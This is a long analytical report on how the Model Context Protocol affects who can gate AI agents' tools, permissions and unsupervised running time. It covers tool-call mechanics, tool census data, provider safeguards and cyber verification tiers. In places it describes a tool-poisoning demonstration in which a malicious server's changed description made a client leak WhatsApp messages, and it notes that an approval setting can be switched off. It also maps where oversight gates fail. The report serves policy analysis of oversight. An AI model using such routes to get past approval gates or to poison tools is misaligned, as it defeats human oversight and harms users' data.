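# Whether open tool standards like the Model Context Protocol make autonomy gates unenforceable

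## How models are connected to tools, and what it means to gate one

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting AI models to other software, such as mailboxes, databases, calendars and web browsers. Anthropic, the company that makes the Claude models, released it in November 2024, and OpenAI, Google and Microsoft have since added support for it to their products. Anyone may write a program that offers tools in MCP's format, and anyone may connect that program to a model without asking the company that trained the model.

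That freedom bears on a precautionary idea about AI agents, which are AI models run in a loop with tools so that their outputs cause actions. The idea is to withhold some tools from an agent until there is reason to trust it with them. If a user can attach almost any tool to almost any model in a few minutes, it is unclear who can still withhold anything. It could be the company that runs the model, the company whose service the tool acts on, the application or employer in between, or the state. Less happens when a model "uses" a tool than the phrase suggests, and comparing these parties requires some knowledge of the process.

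### One tool call, step by step

A language model takes in text and produces text. It cannot open a file or send a message, so another program has to do these things. Anthropic's developer guide *How tool use works* states that the model "never runs anything on its own."

Suppose someone asks an assistant to move Thursday's meeting by emailing a colleague. The person types into a host application, meaning the program a person uses to run the model, which might be a chat app or a code editor. The host application passes the text on to the model provider, the company that runs the model and sells access to it. It does so through an API, the interface through which one program sends requests to another. Along with the person's message, the host application sends a description of each tool on offer. In Anthropic's format, an email tool could look like this:

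```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Sends an email from the user's own account. The message goes out at once and cannot be recalled.",
  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to": { "type": "string" },
      "subject": { "type": "string" },
      "body": { "type": "string" }
    },
    "required": ["to", "subject", "body"]
  }
}
```

Anthropic's *Define tools* explains that the API converts these definitions into prompt text and places them before the conversation, with a line stating that tools are available. The model therefore receives each tool as text in its input. Anthropic advises developers to describe each tool in at least three or four sentences, and considers the description by far the biggest factor in how well the model uses the tool.

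The model now writes its reply. Where a tool fits the task, the reply contains a structured request:

```json
{
  "type": "tool_use",
  "id": "call_01",
  "name": "send_email",
  "input": {
    "to": "ravi@example.com",
    "subject": "Thursday's meeting",
    "body": "Could we move it to 3 pm?"
  }
}
```

At this point, the email has not been sent. The host application reads the request, finds the code that its developer attached to the name `send_email`, and runs it. That code signs in to the mail service and submits the message. The application then adds the result to the conversation as text ("Message sent", or an error) and sends the whole conversation back to the model. The model either writes another request or finishes with a normal answer. An agent is this loop repeated, sometimes for a few rounds and sometimes for hours.

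The model provider receives the tool's description, the model's request and whatever result the program reports, but never the tool's code. A developer could attach the name `save_note` to code that sends email, and the provider could not tell from what it receives.

The loop also doesn't depend on any special tool feature. Some developers use pattern matching to extract a decision from the model's prose. Anthropic sensibly advises them to define a tool instead, but the advice implies that pattern matching works, if clumsily. Any model that can reliably write in a fixed format can use a tool, provided a program reads its output.

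The exceptions are web search, page fetching and a few other tools whose code Anthropic runs on its own machines, so the application receives only the results. A provider can switch off tools like these at any time. But Anthropic says the "vast majority" of tool traffic involves tools that developers define and run themselves.

### What MCP adds

Developers were connecting models to software before MCP existed, but they built a separate connector for each pair. Connecting three applications to five services could require fifteen connectors. With a shared format, it requires three programs and five MCP servers, and each program can connect to any of the servers. In its launch announcement, *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* (2024), Anthropic said the purpose was to replace "fragmented integrations with a single protocol."

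The Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) divides the work among three pieces of software. The host application runs the model's side of the exchange, decides which connections to allow and asks the user for consent. It contains clients, small components that each hold a connection to exactly one server. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to a model in MCP's format. The company that runs the model has no role of its own and appears only as a party the host application deals with, under whatever arrangement the two have.

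A server can be local or remote, which affects who can see it. A local server is a process that the host application starts on the user's machine, and the two exchange messages through the operating system rather than over a network. In the Model Context Protocol's introductory overview, for example, Claude Desktop starts a server that reads and writes the user's files. A remote server runs on someone else's machine, and the client reaches it over HTTP, the protocol that web browsers use. Sentry, a company that tracks software errors, runs one for its customers. An email tool could be either a program the user downloads, which signs in to the mailbox from their laptop, or a server that the mail company runs.

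The host application can discover what a server offers at run time. Its client sends a `tools/list` message, and the server returns names, descriptions and input formats much like the one above. The host application merges the lists from all its servers and shows them to the model. When the model requests `send_email`, the host application finds the server that provides it and sends that server a `tools/call` message with the arguments. The server runs the tool and returns text.

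The tool list can also change while the agent is running. A server may add a tool and notify every client that subscribed to such changes, and each client can then fetch the new list. Any tests run on the agent before the change would not have included the new tool.

The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) requires servers to implement access controls and limit how fast clients can call tools, using the word "must". It only recommends, with a "should", that a human be able to deny a tool call, so a developer who writes a host application with no confirmation prompt has broken only a recommendation. Developers can ignore the requirements too. Bucknall, Byrley and Hammond (2026) point out in *From TCP/IP to MCP* that the people who implement a protocol of this kind remain free to deviate from it, and that it spreads through network effects rather than any mandate.

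MCP's design principles keep the full conversation with the host application and give each server only the context it needs. An email server therefore receives the recipient, subject and body, but not the person's original request or any sign that the model has been doing something alarming with another tool.

### Two years of growth

David Soria Parra pitched the idea for the Model Context Protocol to Justin Spahr-Summers at Anthropic in the summer of 2024, and the company published the protocol on 25 November. Willison (2024), a programmer who had been trying it for a few days, wrote in his launch-day note *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* that the set-up was "pretty clunky" because users had to edit a configuration file by hand and could run servers only on their own machines. His favourite of the thirteen example servers let Claude read from and write to a database on his computer.

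MCP's revision of 26 March 2025 introduced remote servers. On the same day OpenAI, Anthropic's main rival, announced that it would support MCP, first in its agent-building toolkit and later in its API and ChatGPT's desktop app. This meant that a tool built for one company's models would work with the other's. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI adds support for Anthropic’s MCP LLM connectivity protocol* (2025) also relayed Anthropic's claim that building a connection with MCP could take less than an hour in some cases.

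In December 2025 Anthropic donated the protocol to the Agentic AI Foundation, a fund that Anthropic, OpenAI and the payments company Block set up under the non-profit Linux Foundation (*Donating the Model Context Protocol and establishing the Agentic AI Foundation*). The protocol's existing maintainers continued to run the project.

The largest technical change came on 28 July 2026. Until then, a client opened each connection with a handshake, and a remote server could issue a session number that the client had to repeat in every later request. The new version is stateless, meaning that each request carries everything a server needs to answer it, so any available machine can take the next one. The maintainers made the protocol stateless to help it scale, but the new version also makes tool calls easier to control. The Model Context Protocol's release post (2026) explains that a request over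 HTTP must now name the tool in its header, outside the body of the message. A gateway, which is a checkpoint that an organisation places between its agents and their tools, can read the name there and allow or block the call. This helps only with traffic that passes through the gateway, and a host application and a local server on the same laptop exchange no HTTP headers.

Adoption of MCP has been very fast. Its maintainers count downloads of the SDKs, the code libraries that developers use to build clients and servers. *Two Years of MCP Builders* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) reports that monthly downloads rose from more than 90 million in November 2025 to more than 700 million in the thirty days to 23 November 2026. Over 4.5 billion of the 5 billion total downloads came in the past year.

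Downloads are a poor guide to the number of users, since automated systems fetch the same library repeatedly. Figures on use are scarcer but consistent with the download counts. The Agentic AI Foundation reported in *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026) that MCP tool calls from ChatGPT users in August 2026 were 98 times their January level, though it gave no absolute number. It also reported that Resend, a company that sends email on behalf of other software, had passed a million MCP calls in a month. Bucknall and colleagues put the number of distinct tools in the hundreds of thousands.

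### Affordances and gates

An affordance is something a model can do in the world because of the tools and permissions it has been given. It differs from a capability, which is what the model could do if it had the means. *The Loss of Control Playbook* (2025), which takes the term from Sharkey and colleagues, uses email as its example. A model may be able to write a persuasive message, but it cannot email it without access to a mail system. Permissions narrow an affordance further. An agent might be allowed to read a mailbox but not send from it, or to send only to addresses inside the company.

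An autonomy gate is a point at which someone can withhold a tool, a permission or unsupervised running time from an agent until a condition is met. The condition could be a safety test, a period of good behaviour under supervision, a person's approval of each message, or a licence. A restriction without a condition is only a limit, such as the cap Anthropic's servers place on how many rounds of searching or code execution a model may run before they return a paused response. The application can resume the model by sending the conversation back. If Anthropic required a human to review the work before the model could resume, the cap would become a gate on running time.

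One reason to gate tools, rather than only test the model and refuse to release it if it proves dangerous, is that the harm a mistake can do depends partly on which tools the model has. The *Playbook* compares access to email with the ability to create cloud accounts and manage their credentials, which would let an AI system allocate computing resources to itself or widen its own privileges. The same model with the same flaws is a nuisance with email access but could be a serious problem with control of cloud accounts.

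Developers test a model before release with the tools they have thought of, but users keep attaching new ones for as long as the model is in service. With MCP, the list of available tools can change in the middle of a task. A safety case that relies on the model being unable to send anything no longer holds once someone connects a mail server, even if the model hasn't changed.

Tool gates are also easier to adjust. Withdrawing a model affects every customer, including the great majority who were doing nothing risky, while withdrawing one agent's permission to send messages affects only that agent and can be reversed in a moment. A regulator or company that is unsure how far to trust a new model can therefore start with few permissions and add more, without deciding on the whole model in advance.

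However, an agent that stops to wait for approval is less useful to its user, so every gate gives someone a reason to look for a way around it. Some of that pressure may come from the agent itself. The *Playbook* warns that future systems could manipulate poorly informed users into granting them more affordances. Even a model with no tools can have effects through text alone, by persuading a reader to act.

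### Where a call can be stopped

The email to Ravi passes through several hands, and each of them could in principle halt it.

- The model can decline to write the request, because its provider trained it to or because the provider's filters cut the reply short.
- The host application can leave the tool off the list, ask the user first, or simply not carry out the request.
- The MCP server can omit `send_email` from the tools it offers, or answer the call with an error.
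- The underlying service, here the company that hosts the mailbox, can reject the sign-in or refuse to deliver the message.
- The law can require any of these parties to refuse, and punish them or the user if the message goes out anyway.

A power to halt one message is not yet a gate that works. The user may just send the next message by another route.

### Three tests of enforceability

In this report, a gate is enforceable only if its holder can see the connection, can refuse it, and by refusing withholds the affordance, because the substitutes are harder to obtain or work less well. An example of a gate is a rule that no agent may send mail from a person's account until that person has read the message.

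Whether the company that hosts the mailbox can detect the agent depends on how the agent gets access. Services commonly issue an access token, a credential for one program that comes with a list of permitted actions, called its scope. If the email server uses a token, the company can tell which program is calling and that it is trying to send mail, but not whether a person or a model chose the words. If the user has instead given a local server an ordinary password, the traffic may look much like the person's own. Blocking the agent is easier than detecting it, because the company can cancel the token or issue one that allows reading but not sending.

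Whether the refusal withholds anything depends on the exact affordance. The agent could open an account with another mail company and write to Ravi from there, but Ravi would get a message from an address he has never seen. If the worry is an agent that speaks in its user's name, to colleagues or a bank, the gate passes the third test, because no other company can supply that address. The same gate fails the test if the worry is fraudulent mail to strangers, where the refusal achieves little because almost any address will do.

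The host application carries out the tool calls, so it has the best view of them and can block one by not executing it. But a user who dislikes the confirmation prompt can install a different application, unless someone else, such as an employer, controls what runs on the machine.

As long as the developer has labelled the tool honestly, the model provider sees the description and the request as they pass through its API. It can also refuse the request. But many models can write a two-line email, so a refusal barely hinders the user. It would hinder the user far more if only the two or three strongest models could do the task.

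The model can always draft the message instead and leave a person to paste it into the mailbox and send it. This does not defeat the gate, because the gate is meant to stop the model from sending email unsupervised, and here a person handles the message before it goes out.

### Enforceable and impossible to evade

A gate can be enforceable even if some people get round it. Hardly any rule would count as enforceable otherwise. In most countries, for example, a pharmacist may not hand over morphine without a prescription. The pharmacist can enforce this rule because customers have to come to the counter to ask for the drug, and the pharmacist can refuse them. Some people get round the rule by forging prescriptions, using up a relative's leftover tablets or buying from a dealer. But those routes are dangerous, unreliable or criminal, and most people who might want the drug never try them.

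A website that asks visitors to click a button confirming that they are over eighteen has no way to check their age. It can refuse those who click "no", but they can go back and click "yes", so the rule keeps nobody out, even if it is as well meant as the one at the pharmacy.

How often a gate can acceptably fail depends on the harm it is meant to prevent. If the danger is thousands of careless users whose agents send embarrassing or costly messages, a gate that stops nine in ten of them prevents most of the damage. But if one determined person with an unsupervised agent could cause a catastrophe, stopping nine in ten is not nearly enough, and the one who gets through is likely to be the one who tried hardest. Anyone arguing that tool gates do or do not work should therefore specify whom the gates are meant to stop.

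An open standard can also weaken a gate on the third test, by making substitutes easier to get. When every connection between a model and a service was a custom job, a user whose application refused to connect to a mailbox had to find a programmer or give up. With MCP, the user can look for a server that somebody else has already written or, failing that, have a model write one. At the 2024 launch, Anthropic was already advertising Claude 3.5 Sonnet as "adept at quickly building MCP server implementations."

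## The case that open standards leave no gate

If a standard makes almost every tool easy to replace, perhaps nobody can withhold one any more. Set out in steps, the argument is:

1. Anyone may write an MCP server and connect it to a model without asking permission.
2. The protocol does not enforce its own rules on consent.
3. The model provider sees a tool's description but not what the tool really does.
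4. People and their AI assistants now produce tools faster than anyone can review them.
5. So no one is placed to withhold an affordance from an agent.

This case is a reconstruction, since several writers hold parts of it without drawing the conclusion. The US National Security Agency's guidance paper *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) describes the protocol as having spread faster than its security model developed, but it also recommends controls. Syed (2026), in *Security Considerations for Model Context Protocol (MCP) Implementations in AI Agent Systems*, argues that the specification sets no binding security requirements, and then proposes some. Stein (2026), a researcher at the UK AI Security Institute, comes closest in *How are AI agents used?*, warning that once agents build tools for other agents, tool creation "may scale beyond human oversight." Yet Stein also suggests that developers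 and regulators could require human authentication for large financial transfers, which would be pointless if nobody could block a transfer.

### Anyone can write a server

Nobody needs a license to publish an MCP server. On 5 December 2024, ten days after MCP's release, somebody published an unofficial Google Calendar server on the code-sharing site GitHub. As Stein points out, Anthropic did not add a ready-made calendar tool to its own chat product until April 2025, and OpenAI did not until August. For about four months, Claude users could therefore get a calendar tool from a stranger's code that they could not yet get from Anthropic.

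Employers had little more warning than the labs. McLuckie (2026), a software executive writing for the Agentic AI Foundation, recalls that at most of the companies he had talked to, developers "wired a dozen servers into their coding agents" before the teams responsible for internal systems could ask a question. This is his impression, not a count, and his article introduces the July 2026 version of MCP, which he believes lets those teams govern MCP like the rest of their infrastructure. Even so, nobody disputes the first premise of the argument.

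### What the specification cannot enforce

The Model Context Protocol's overview page lists principles that would put a gate in front of every tool call if everyone followed them. Users must explicitly consent to all data access and operations, and host applications must obtain that consent before invoking any tool. But the maintainers concede on the same page that "MCP itself cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level."

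That was the wording in November 2025. The maintainers kept the sentence word for word in the June 2026 draft of the Model Context Protocol's July version, and the protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), which lists the July changes, mentions no edit to it. The draft dropped one principle, which required the user's approval when a server requests text from the host application's model. The July version is phasing out these requests, but they will keep working for at least a year.

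The consent principles are also weaker than they look, because they use "must" in lower case and the overview page treats the word as a formal requirement only when it is in capitals. The advice after the disclaimer is only a recommendation.

Writing the consent rule as a capitalized requirement would not help much, because a person gives consent on a screen that the server cannot see, inside the host application. The July version does let a server interrupt a call by returning a request for input, and the host application then repeats the call with the answer attached. In the Model Context Protocol's release post, a manager at the database company Supabase welcomes this as a way to check with the user before a query deletes data. But the server cannot tell who answered, and a developer could write a host application that accepts every such request automatically.

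The rules on authorization, the process by which a program shows that it may use a service, are similarly permissive. They cover only HTTP connections, according to the Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2025), and the NSA notes that developers may omit authorization even there. The July rules of the Model Context Protocol (2026) require every implementation to support the basic message format, versioning and message patterns, and make the other components optional.

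Syed goes too far, though, in claiming that the specification has no binding security requirements. The Model Context Protocol's page on tools requires servers, with a capitalised "MUST", to validate inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise outputs. None of these requirements concerns human approval, and a server that ignores all four still works. Researchers at Akamai, which sells network security, similarly conclude that the July version removes several old weaknesses, such as session hijacking, but leaves developers to build the critical security boundaries themselves.

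So the protocol is not a gate, and the second premise is true. But people who use a protocol may still be able to enforce rules that the protocol can't. The protocol that carries email between mail companies has never been able to stop spam, for example, but the companies keep most of it out of people's inboxes. MCP's maintainers evidently intend a similar division of labour, because in the same sentence as the disclaimer they ask developers to build consent flows and access controls into their applications.

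### The description and the tool

The model provider cannot tell when a tool named `save_note` really sends email. Under the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the host application and its user are in much the same position, since they too rely on the server's description of its tools. A server can add optional annotations that describe a tool's behavior, such as whether it only reads data. MCP requires clients to treat these annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. That is sensible, but it leaves a client with little reliable information about a new server's tools.

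The NSA recounts a demonstration in which researchers connected a client to two servers, a trusted one that handled WhatsApp messages and a malicious one of their own. The malicious server showed a harmless tool description at installation and switched to a hostile one after its second use. The new description caused the client to expose the user's WhatsApp messages, and the user received no notice or request for approval.

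An approval can become outdated even when the server's operator isn't malicious. The NSA warns that an already trusted server can often gain new capabilities or reach new data without anyone approving the change. A person who clicked "allow" in March may be running a very different tool by May. Some tools can also do more from the start than their descriptions suggest. Syed lists file tools that can read folders beyond those their stated purpose requires, but doesn't count how many servers have this fault.

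These cases support the third premise, but in most of them the user is a victim. A user who wants an agent to send email despite a gate has a different problem. The model has to know that `save_note` sends email before it can use it that way, so someone has to explain this in the tool's description or in the conversation, and the provider receives both. The provider also receives the call's arguments, which would include an address, a subject line and a message. A careful user could disguise all of this, but the model would then have to interpret the disguised instructions and arguments, and it would probably make more mistakes.

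### More tools than reviewers

The main evidence for the fourth premise is Stein's study. Stein searched GitHub and Smithery, a large registry where users or applications pick MCP servers, and found 73,338 candidate servers published between November 2024 and February 2026. Stein removed duplicates and projects that no GitHub user had starred, had the language model Claude Sonnet 4.5 check that each remaining entry was an MCP server, and kept only those with clearly described tools. That left 19,388 servers offering 177,436 tools.

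Claude Sonnet 4.5 then sorted the tools into three kinds. Perception tools read data, reasoning tools analyse it, and action tools change something outside the model, for example by editing a file or sending an email. As a check, fourteen experts labelled 100 tools each and agreed with the model 81% of the time, or 78% according to one of the study's captions. Stein estimated use from download counts on NPM and PyPI, the standard public code libraries for JavaScript and Python.

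| What Stein measured | Earlier | February 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Public MCP tools | about 4,888 (January 2025) | about 177,000 |
| Server downloads per month | 0.08 million (January 2025) | 14 million |
| Action tools' share of downloads | 27% (November 2024) | 65% |
| The same share for registered companies' tools | 21% (November 2024) | 71% |
| New servers with signs of AI assistance | 6% (January 2025) | 62% |

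The number of public tools grew 36-fold in thirteen months. The shift towards action tools matters more for gates than this growth, because an agent that can only read does less direct damage. General-purpose tools, such as those that control a web browser, account for most of that shift. Most action tools support medium-stakes work, such as administering computer systems, although Stein also found fast growth in tools that make payments.

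The download figures have serious limits. Most importantly, a download shows that a program fetched a server's code, not that an agent used any of its tools. A developer who sets up a fresh virtual machine every morning may add a download each time, while someone who adds a ready-made connector in the Claude app adds none. Stein could match only 3,854 of the 19,388 servers to download data. The method also counts each installation as one use of every tool on the server, so a person who installs a thirty-tool server to use one tool adds thirty uses. The 65% therefore describes the tools on the servers that developers installed, and Stein suggests that it may mostly reflect what developers were trying out.

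The tool counts are more reliable but still need some care, because Stein examined each server only once, in October 2025 or February 2026. The January 2025 figure therefore counts the tools that the earliest servers had some months later, and it misses any server whose author had deleted it by then.

The rise in AI-assisted servers probably reflects both greater use of coding agents and better labelling of their work. Stein counted a server as AI-assisted if its first month of public history contained any trace of a coding agent, such as a line crediting the agent as co-author or a configuration file for one. This misses help that left no trace and includes servers to which an agent may have contributed very little. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, accounts for 69% of the servers detected. It came out only in February 2025 and by default credits itself in the changes it makes, so some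 of the climb from 6% may come from better labelling. Labelling alone is unlikely to explain a tenfold rise.

The public stock of tools grew by about 172,500 in thirteen months, or roughly 440 a day. If each review took an hour, 55 people working eight-hour days, weekends included, could keep up. Large social networks employ far more people than that, in the thousands, to check posts. The volume is less of an obstacle than the lack of any point that every tool has to pass through. Reviewers also cannot know what a server will do after they approve it.

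Use is also far more concentrated than publication. Registered companies such as Stripe, Google and GitHub publish 8,469 of the tools in Stein's collection, less than 5%, but their servers account for 45 million of the 78 million downloads. A reviewer who checked those tools, about one in twenty, would cover more than half of what people install. Reviewers could also use AI. Stein had a model sort the whole collection, with disagreement on one tool in five. That would be far too much for a safety review, but newer models could presumably do better, and could read the code as well as the description.

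Although nobody reviews every tool, someone could review most of the ones people use. That would be enough if the worry is careless users who install whatever is popular. It would do little to stop someone who seeks out an obscure server that does what the popular ones block, or who has a model write one.

### The step to the conclusion

The conclusion does not follow even if all four premises are true. The first premise rules out a licensor of servers as a gatekeeper, and the second rules out the protocol's maintainers. The third casts doubt on the model provider, and the fourth on reviewers. None of them covers the service that the tool acts on. The unofficial calendar server of December 2024 needed nobody's permission to exist, but it could do nothing for a user until Google gave it access to that user's calendar. The premises also leave out the state and employers, who may control what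 runs on their machines. The argument needs a fifth premise, that none of these parties can refuse either, and the protocol's openness to anyone with a laptop does not establish that.

Another, more basic reply is that MCP made little difference, even if the premises are true. On this view, MCP made it easier to connect agents to tools but gave agents no new abilities, because they could already do the same things without an MCP server.

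### Connecting tools before MCP

The history supports the reply. LangChain, an open-source library released in October 2022, came with ready-made tools such as web search. It asked the model to write its chosen action in a fixed text format and ran whatever the model wrote. In March 2023, some twenty months before MCP, a game developer released Auto-GPT, a program that ran OpenAI's GPT-4 in a loop with access to the web, files and code execution. By default, Auto-GPT asked the user to approve each step, but a "continuous" setting switched the approvals off, so anyone who could install the program could remove an autonomy gate by changing one option.

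In June 2023 OpenAI added function calling to its API, which let developers send tool descriptions and receive structured requests, as in the email example. OpenAI never saw the code behind the tools, so the third premise was as true in 2023 as it is now.

OpenAI announced ChatGPT plugins in March 2023. A company that wanted ChatGPT to use its service published a machine-readable description of its API, and OpenAI reviewed the plugin before listing it in a store inside ChatGPT. Users could switch on up to three plugins at a time. One of the first plugins came from Zapier, a company that links other companies' software, and connected ChatGPT to more than 5,000 applications, including Gmail. By the summer of 2023, models could already send email, browse the web and run code on a user's laptop.

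MCP is only one route among several. Stein gives the example of ChatGPT, which can reach a user's Google Drive files through a dedicated Drive tool, through a browser if the user hands over a password, or through a code-running tool if the user supplies an access token. Abolishing MCP would leave all three routes open, although developers would have to build the dedicated tool another way.

### Two thousand connectors or 210 adapters

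The cost that MCP lowered was nevertheless large. Suppose that the makers of 10 applications want to connect each of them to 200 tools. With custom connectors, that takes:

10 × 200 = 2,000 connectors

With a shared format, one adapter for each application and one for each tool are enough:

10 + 200 = 210 adapters

The gap widens as the numbers grow, because the first total is a product and the second is a sum. A 201st tool needs ten more connectors under the old arrangement but only one more adapter under the new one. This helps explain why the supply of tools could grow so fast.

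But these totals measure the work of connecting every agent to every tool. Connecting one agent to one mailbox takes only one connector, just as it did in 2023. If a competent programmer could write that connector in two days, the work wouldn't have stopped a criminal group or a hobbyist with a free weekend. It would have stopped people who couldn't program and programmers who didn't care enough to bother.

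Coding agents would also have reduced the work of connecting tools without any standard. At two days each, writing the 2,000 custom connectors by hand takes 4,000 working days, and writing the 210 adapters takes 420. If a coding agent cut each job to one hour, all 2,000 connectors would take 250 eight-hour days, less than the adapters take by hand. These times are invented, but most new servers show traces of coding agents, so it is hard to doubt that agents reduce the work. Stein expects that counting public tools will stop being useful if agents start building their own as they need them. A ban on MCP would then inconvenience software companies but hardly slow down an agent.

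### Whether the lost obstacles were gates

The friction that MCP removed was never an autonomy gate, because nobody controlled it and there was no condition an agent could meet to have it lifted. An agent with a spotless safety record needed the same two days of programming as a reckless one. Similarly, a bad road to a pharmacy keeps some customers away, mostly the ones who want the drug least, but it doesn't limit the drug to people with prescriptions.

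Bad roads do make a pharmacist's refusal more effective, though, if the next pharmacy is fifty miles away. In the same way, real gates were more effective when connectors were hard to build, so the reply involves a larger concession than it seems to. If a gate depended on that difficulty, making connection easier weakened it. How much it weakened depends on whom the gate was meant to stop. The difficulty was a substantial obstacle for careless users who couldn't program, but it barely hindered a determined programmer, so MCP made almost no difference to gates meant to stop programmers.

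OpenAI's plugin review came closer to being a gate, because OpenAI could see which plugins companies submitted and refuse to list them. A refusal kept a plugin from ChatGPT users who couldn't program, but developers could still connect whatever they liked through the API. OpenAI also reviewed each plugin as a whole, so approving Zapier's let in thousands of applications at once and left the checks on what ChatGPT did in each of them largely to Zapier.

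OpenAI ended its plugin review when it closed the plugin store in April 2024, seven months before MCP existed. By then it had already introduced custom versions of ChatGPT that their builders could connect to outside services. But MCP makes such a review easier to bypass if anyone wants to bring it back. In 2023, a ChatGPT user who wanted a tool that OpenAI had rejected had to write a program, but today they can install another application that accepts any MCP server.

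## The case that the model provider still holds the gate

Any agent application a person installs still needs a model. The companies that trained the strongest models run them on their own computers, or on those of a few cloud partners, and sell access through an API instead of releasing copies. An agent built on such a model depends on the provider for every decision, so the provider can stop it even if third parties wrote all of its tools. This argument doesn't cover open-weight models, which anyone with the hardware can download and run.

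### What passes through the provider

The provider sees more of an agent's work than any single MCP server does. The mail server in the email example receives only the message, whereas the provider receives the whole conversation in every round, including the results so far from the agent's other tools. Suppose an agent reads a list of leaked passwords with one tool and tries them on a login page with another. Each server handles only one of these steps, but the provider receives both in the same conversation.

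The provider also gets many chances to stop an agent. An agent that makes 200 tool calls in sequence sends its provider about 200 requests. If the provider refuses the 120th, the agent stops, because the host application has no further tool call to carry out. Unlike the approval prompt in Auto-GPT, which users could switch off with one setting, the provider's controls run on machines that users can't alter.

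A provider has six main ways to use this position. They differ in whether they gate a tool, a use or a user.

| Lever | How it works | What it gates |
|---|---|---|
| Trained refusals | The provider trains the model to decline certain requests, so it never writes the tool call | A use |
| Classifiers | Separate programs sort the text going in and out, and block the reply or send the request to a weaker model | A use |
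| Rate limits | The provider caps how much an account can do in a given time | The amount of use |
| Verification | Customers prove who they are and what work they do before the provider relaxes its safeguards | A user |
| Suspension | The provider closes an account | A user |
| Application rules | The provider decides which host applications may connect, and on what terms | An application, with every tool attached to it |

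None of these gates the tool itself, unless the provider runs it, as Anthropic does with web search. A provider could reject every request that lists a tool called `send_email`, but the developer could just rename the tool. The provider does control whether the model will use a tool. For example, the model can refuse to scan a stranger's computers even while a network scanner stays connected to the agent.

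That is enough to keep a model from breaking into computers, since it can refuse to use any scanner, but not to enforce a rule that no agent may send mail from a person's account until that person has read the message. The person gives approval inside the host application, after the model has written its request and before the result comes back. The provider receives the request and later the words "Message sent", and can't tell from either whether anybody read the email. It could stop the model from sending mail at all, but it would have to rely on the application to make sure the person reads each message first.

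Rate limits are a crude way to gate how long an agent runs. Axios' *Anthropic tightens Claude limits and OpenAI courts defectors* (2026) contrasts a person, who might send dozens or hundreds of prompts a day, with a coding agent that can generate thousands of requests. A cap low enough to hold every agent to a human pace would make ordinary coding agents useless. A provider could instead raise the cap for agents with a good record, which would be a real autonomy gate, but today's caps mostly depend on what the customer pays.

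### Judging a request by its text

Refusals and classifiers rely on text, which often doesn't show whether a request is harmful. A tester hired by a hospital to probe its defences may ask for the same scans, in the same order, as a criminal trying to break into it. Only the tester has the hospital's permission, which no tool call contains.

Misuse is also rare, which makes even a good classifier wrong most of the time it raises an alarm. Suppose that ten sessions in a million are malicious, and that a classifier catches 90% of those and wrongly flags 1% of the rest. These figures are invented, but the pattern holds for any rare offence:

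Correct flags: 90% × 10 = 9

False flags: 1% × 999,990 ≈ 10,000

Only about one flag in 1,100 is correct. A provider that closed every flagged account would ban about 1,100 innocent customers for each criminal, so the penalty for a flag has to be mild.

Anthropic chose a mild safeguard when it launched Claude Fable 5 in June 2026. If a query touched certain topics, a weaker model, Claude Opus 4.8, answered it instead. According to Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* (2026), this happened in fewer than 5% of sessions on average, and the company admitted that some of the redirected requests were harmless. Two months later, according to Constantin's *Anthropic loosens Claude Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026), it cut the model's biology blocks by about 85% to reduce false alarms but kept blocking work such as virology and toxicology. Presumably Anthropic had concluded that most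 of the biology requests it had been blocking were safe to allow.

Programmers have run into the same problem. *I’m Sorry Dave, This Request Triggered Restrictions On Violative Cyber Content* (2026) describes a request that Claude Code blocked in April 2026. The writer had asked it to look for interesting patterns in the settings for git hooks, which are scripts that run automatically when a programmer saves or shares code. The error message suggested applying to Anthropic's verification program.

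### Checking the user instead

A provider can get around the problem by verifying the user as well as checking the request. Axios' *OpenAI opens powerful cyber tools to verified users* (April 2026) described OpenAI as shifting from restricting what its models can do to checking who gets the most sensitive capabilities.

On 9 November 2026, Anthropic released the same underlying model under two names, Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2, at the same price. According to Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026), Fable has strong cybersecurity and biology safeguards and is open to all users, while organisations in cybersecurity or biomedical research can apply for Mythos. Anthropic's approval therefore mainly gives a customer permission rather than a different model.

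For security work, that permission comes in three tiers, which Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* sets out:

| Tier | Work it permits | Who can apply | Approved users |
|---|---|---|---|
| Defense Access | Responding to attacks, analysing malware, confirming reported flaws | Organisations and individuals | No default limit |
| Red Team Access | Authorised break-in tests, writing attack code | Organisations | Up to 75 |
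| Specialized Access | Authorised tests of critical systems, such as power grids | Organisations, which Anthropic reviews with the US government | Up to 25 |

Individuals must have a government photo ID ready and may have to take a live selfie. A company's own red team, staff who attack its systems to find weaknesses, must confirm that someone with authority over the systems approves each test in advance. Anthropic also asks for evidence of the team's skill, such as professional certificates, and an assurance that the organisation runs background checks. Every tier prohibits some acts, including extortion and the mass destruction of data. Anthropic can narrow or withdraw access at any time. On its developer platform, an organisation that exceeds its limit of 75 or 25 users loses access in every workspace until it is back within the limit.

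OpenAI runs a similar scheme, Trusted Access for Cyber. Its overview page lists three levels: GPT-5.5 with standard safeguards, the same model with more precise safeguards for verified defenders, and GPT-5.5-Cyber for authorised offensive testing. A contract doesn't guarantee access to GPT-5.5-Cyber. OpenAI has since reorganised the scheme, and its *Trusted Access for Cyber common issues and troubleshooting* lists the newer tiers as Daybreak Blue and Daybreak Red. Individuals go through a government ID check. Since 1 September 2026 they have also had to sign in with a hardware-backed passkey, a credential tied to a physical device, according to Biometric Update's *OpenAI requires hardware-backed passkeys for trusted cyber access*. Members who don't do so keep ChatGPT but drop back to standard access.

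These schemes are working gates, because each company withholds a permission until the customer meets its conditions. But the conditions concern the customer, and proof that a customer is a bank's security team is no evidence that the model will behave well once it has the bank's credentials. The tiers also differ in what kinds of work the model will do, not in how long it may work unsupervised. Verification is therefore better suited to preventing criminal use than to preventing an agent from misbehaving while it works for an honest customer.

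A provider also has to know who its users are, but it may lack that information. Shortly after Anthropic released Fable 5 and Mythos 5 in June 2026, the US government blocked both models for foreign users. Techzine's *Anthropic may require identity verification for Claude use* reports that Anthropic couldn't immediately verify anyone's identity, so it withdrew both models from everybody. It then revised its policy to let it ask consumers for ID, but the revision didn't cover business customers or API users, and developers build most of their own agents on the API.

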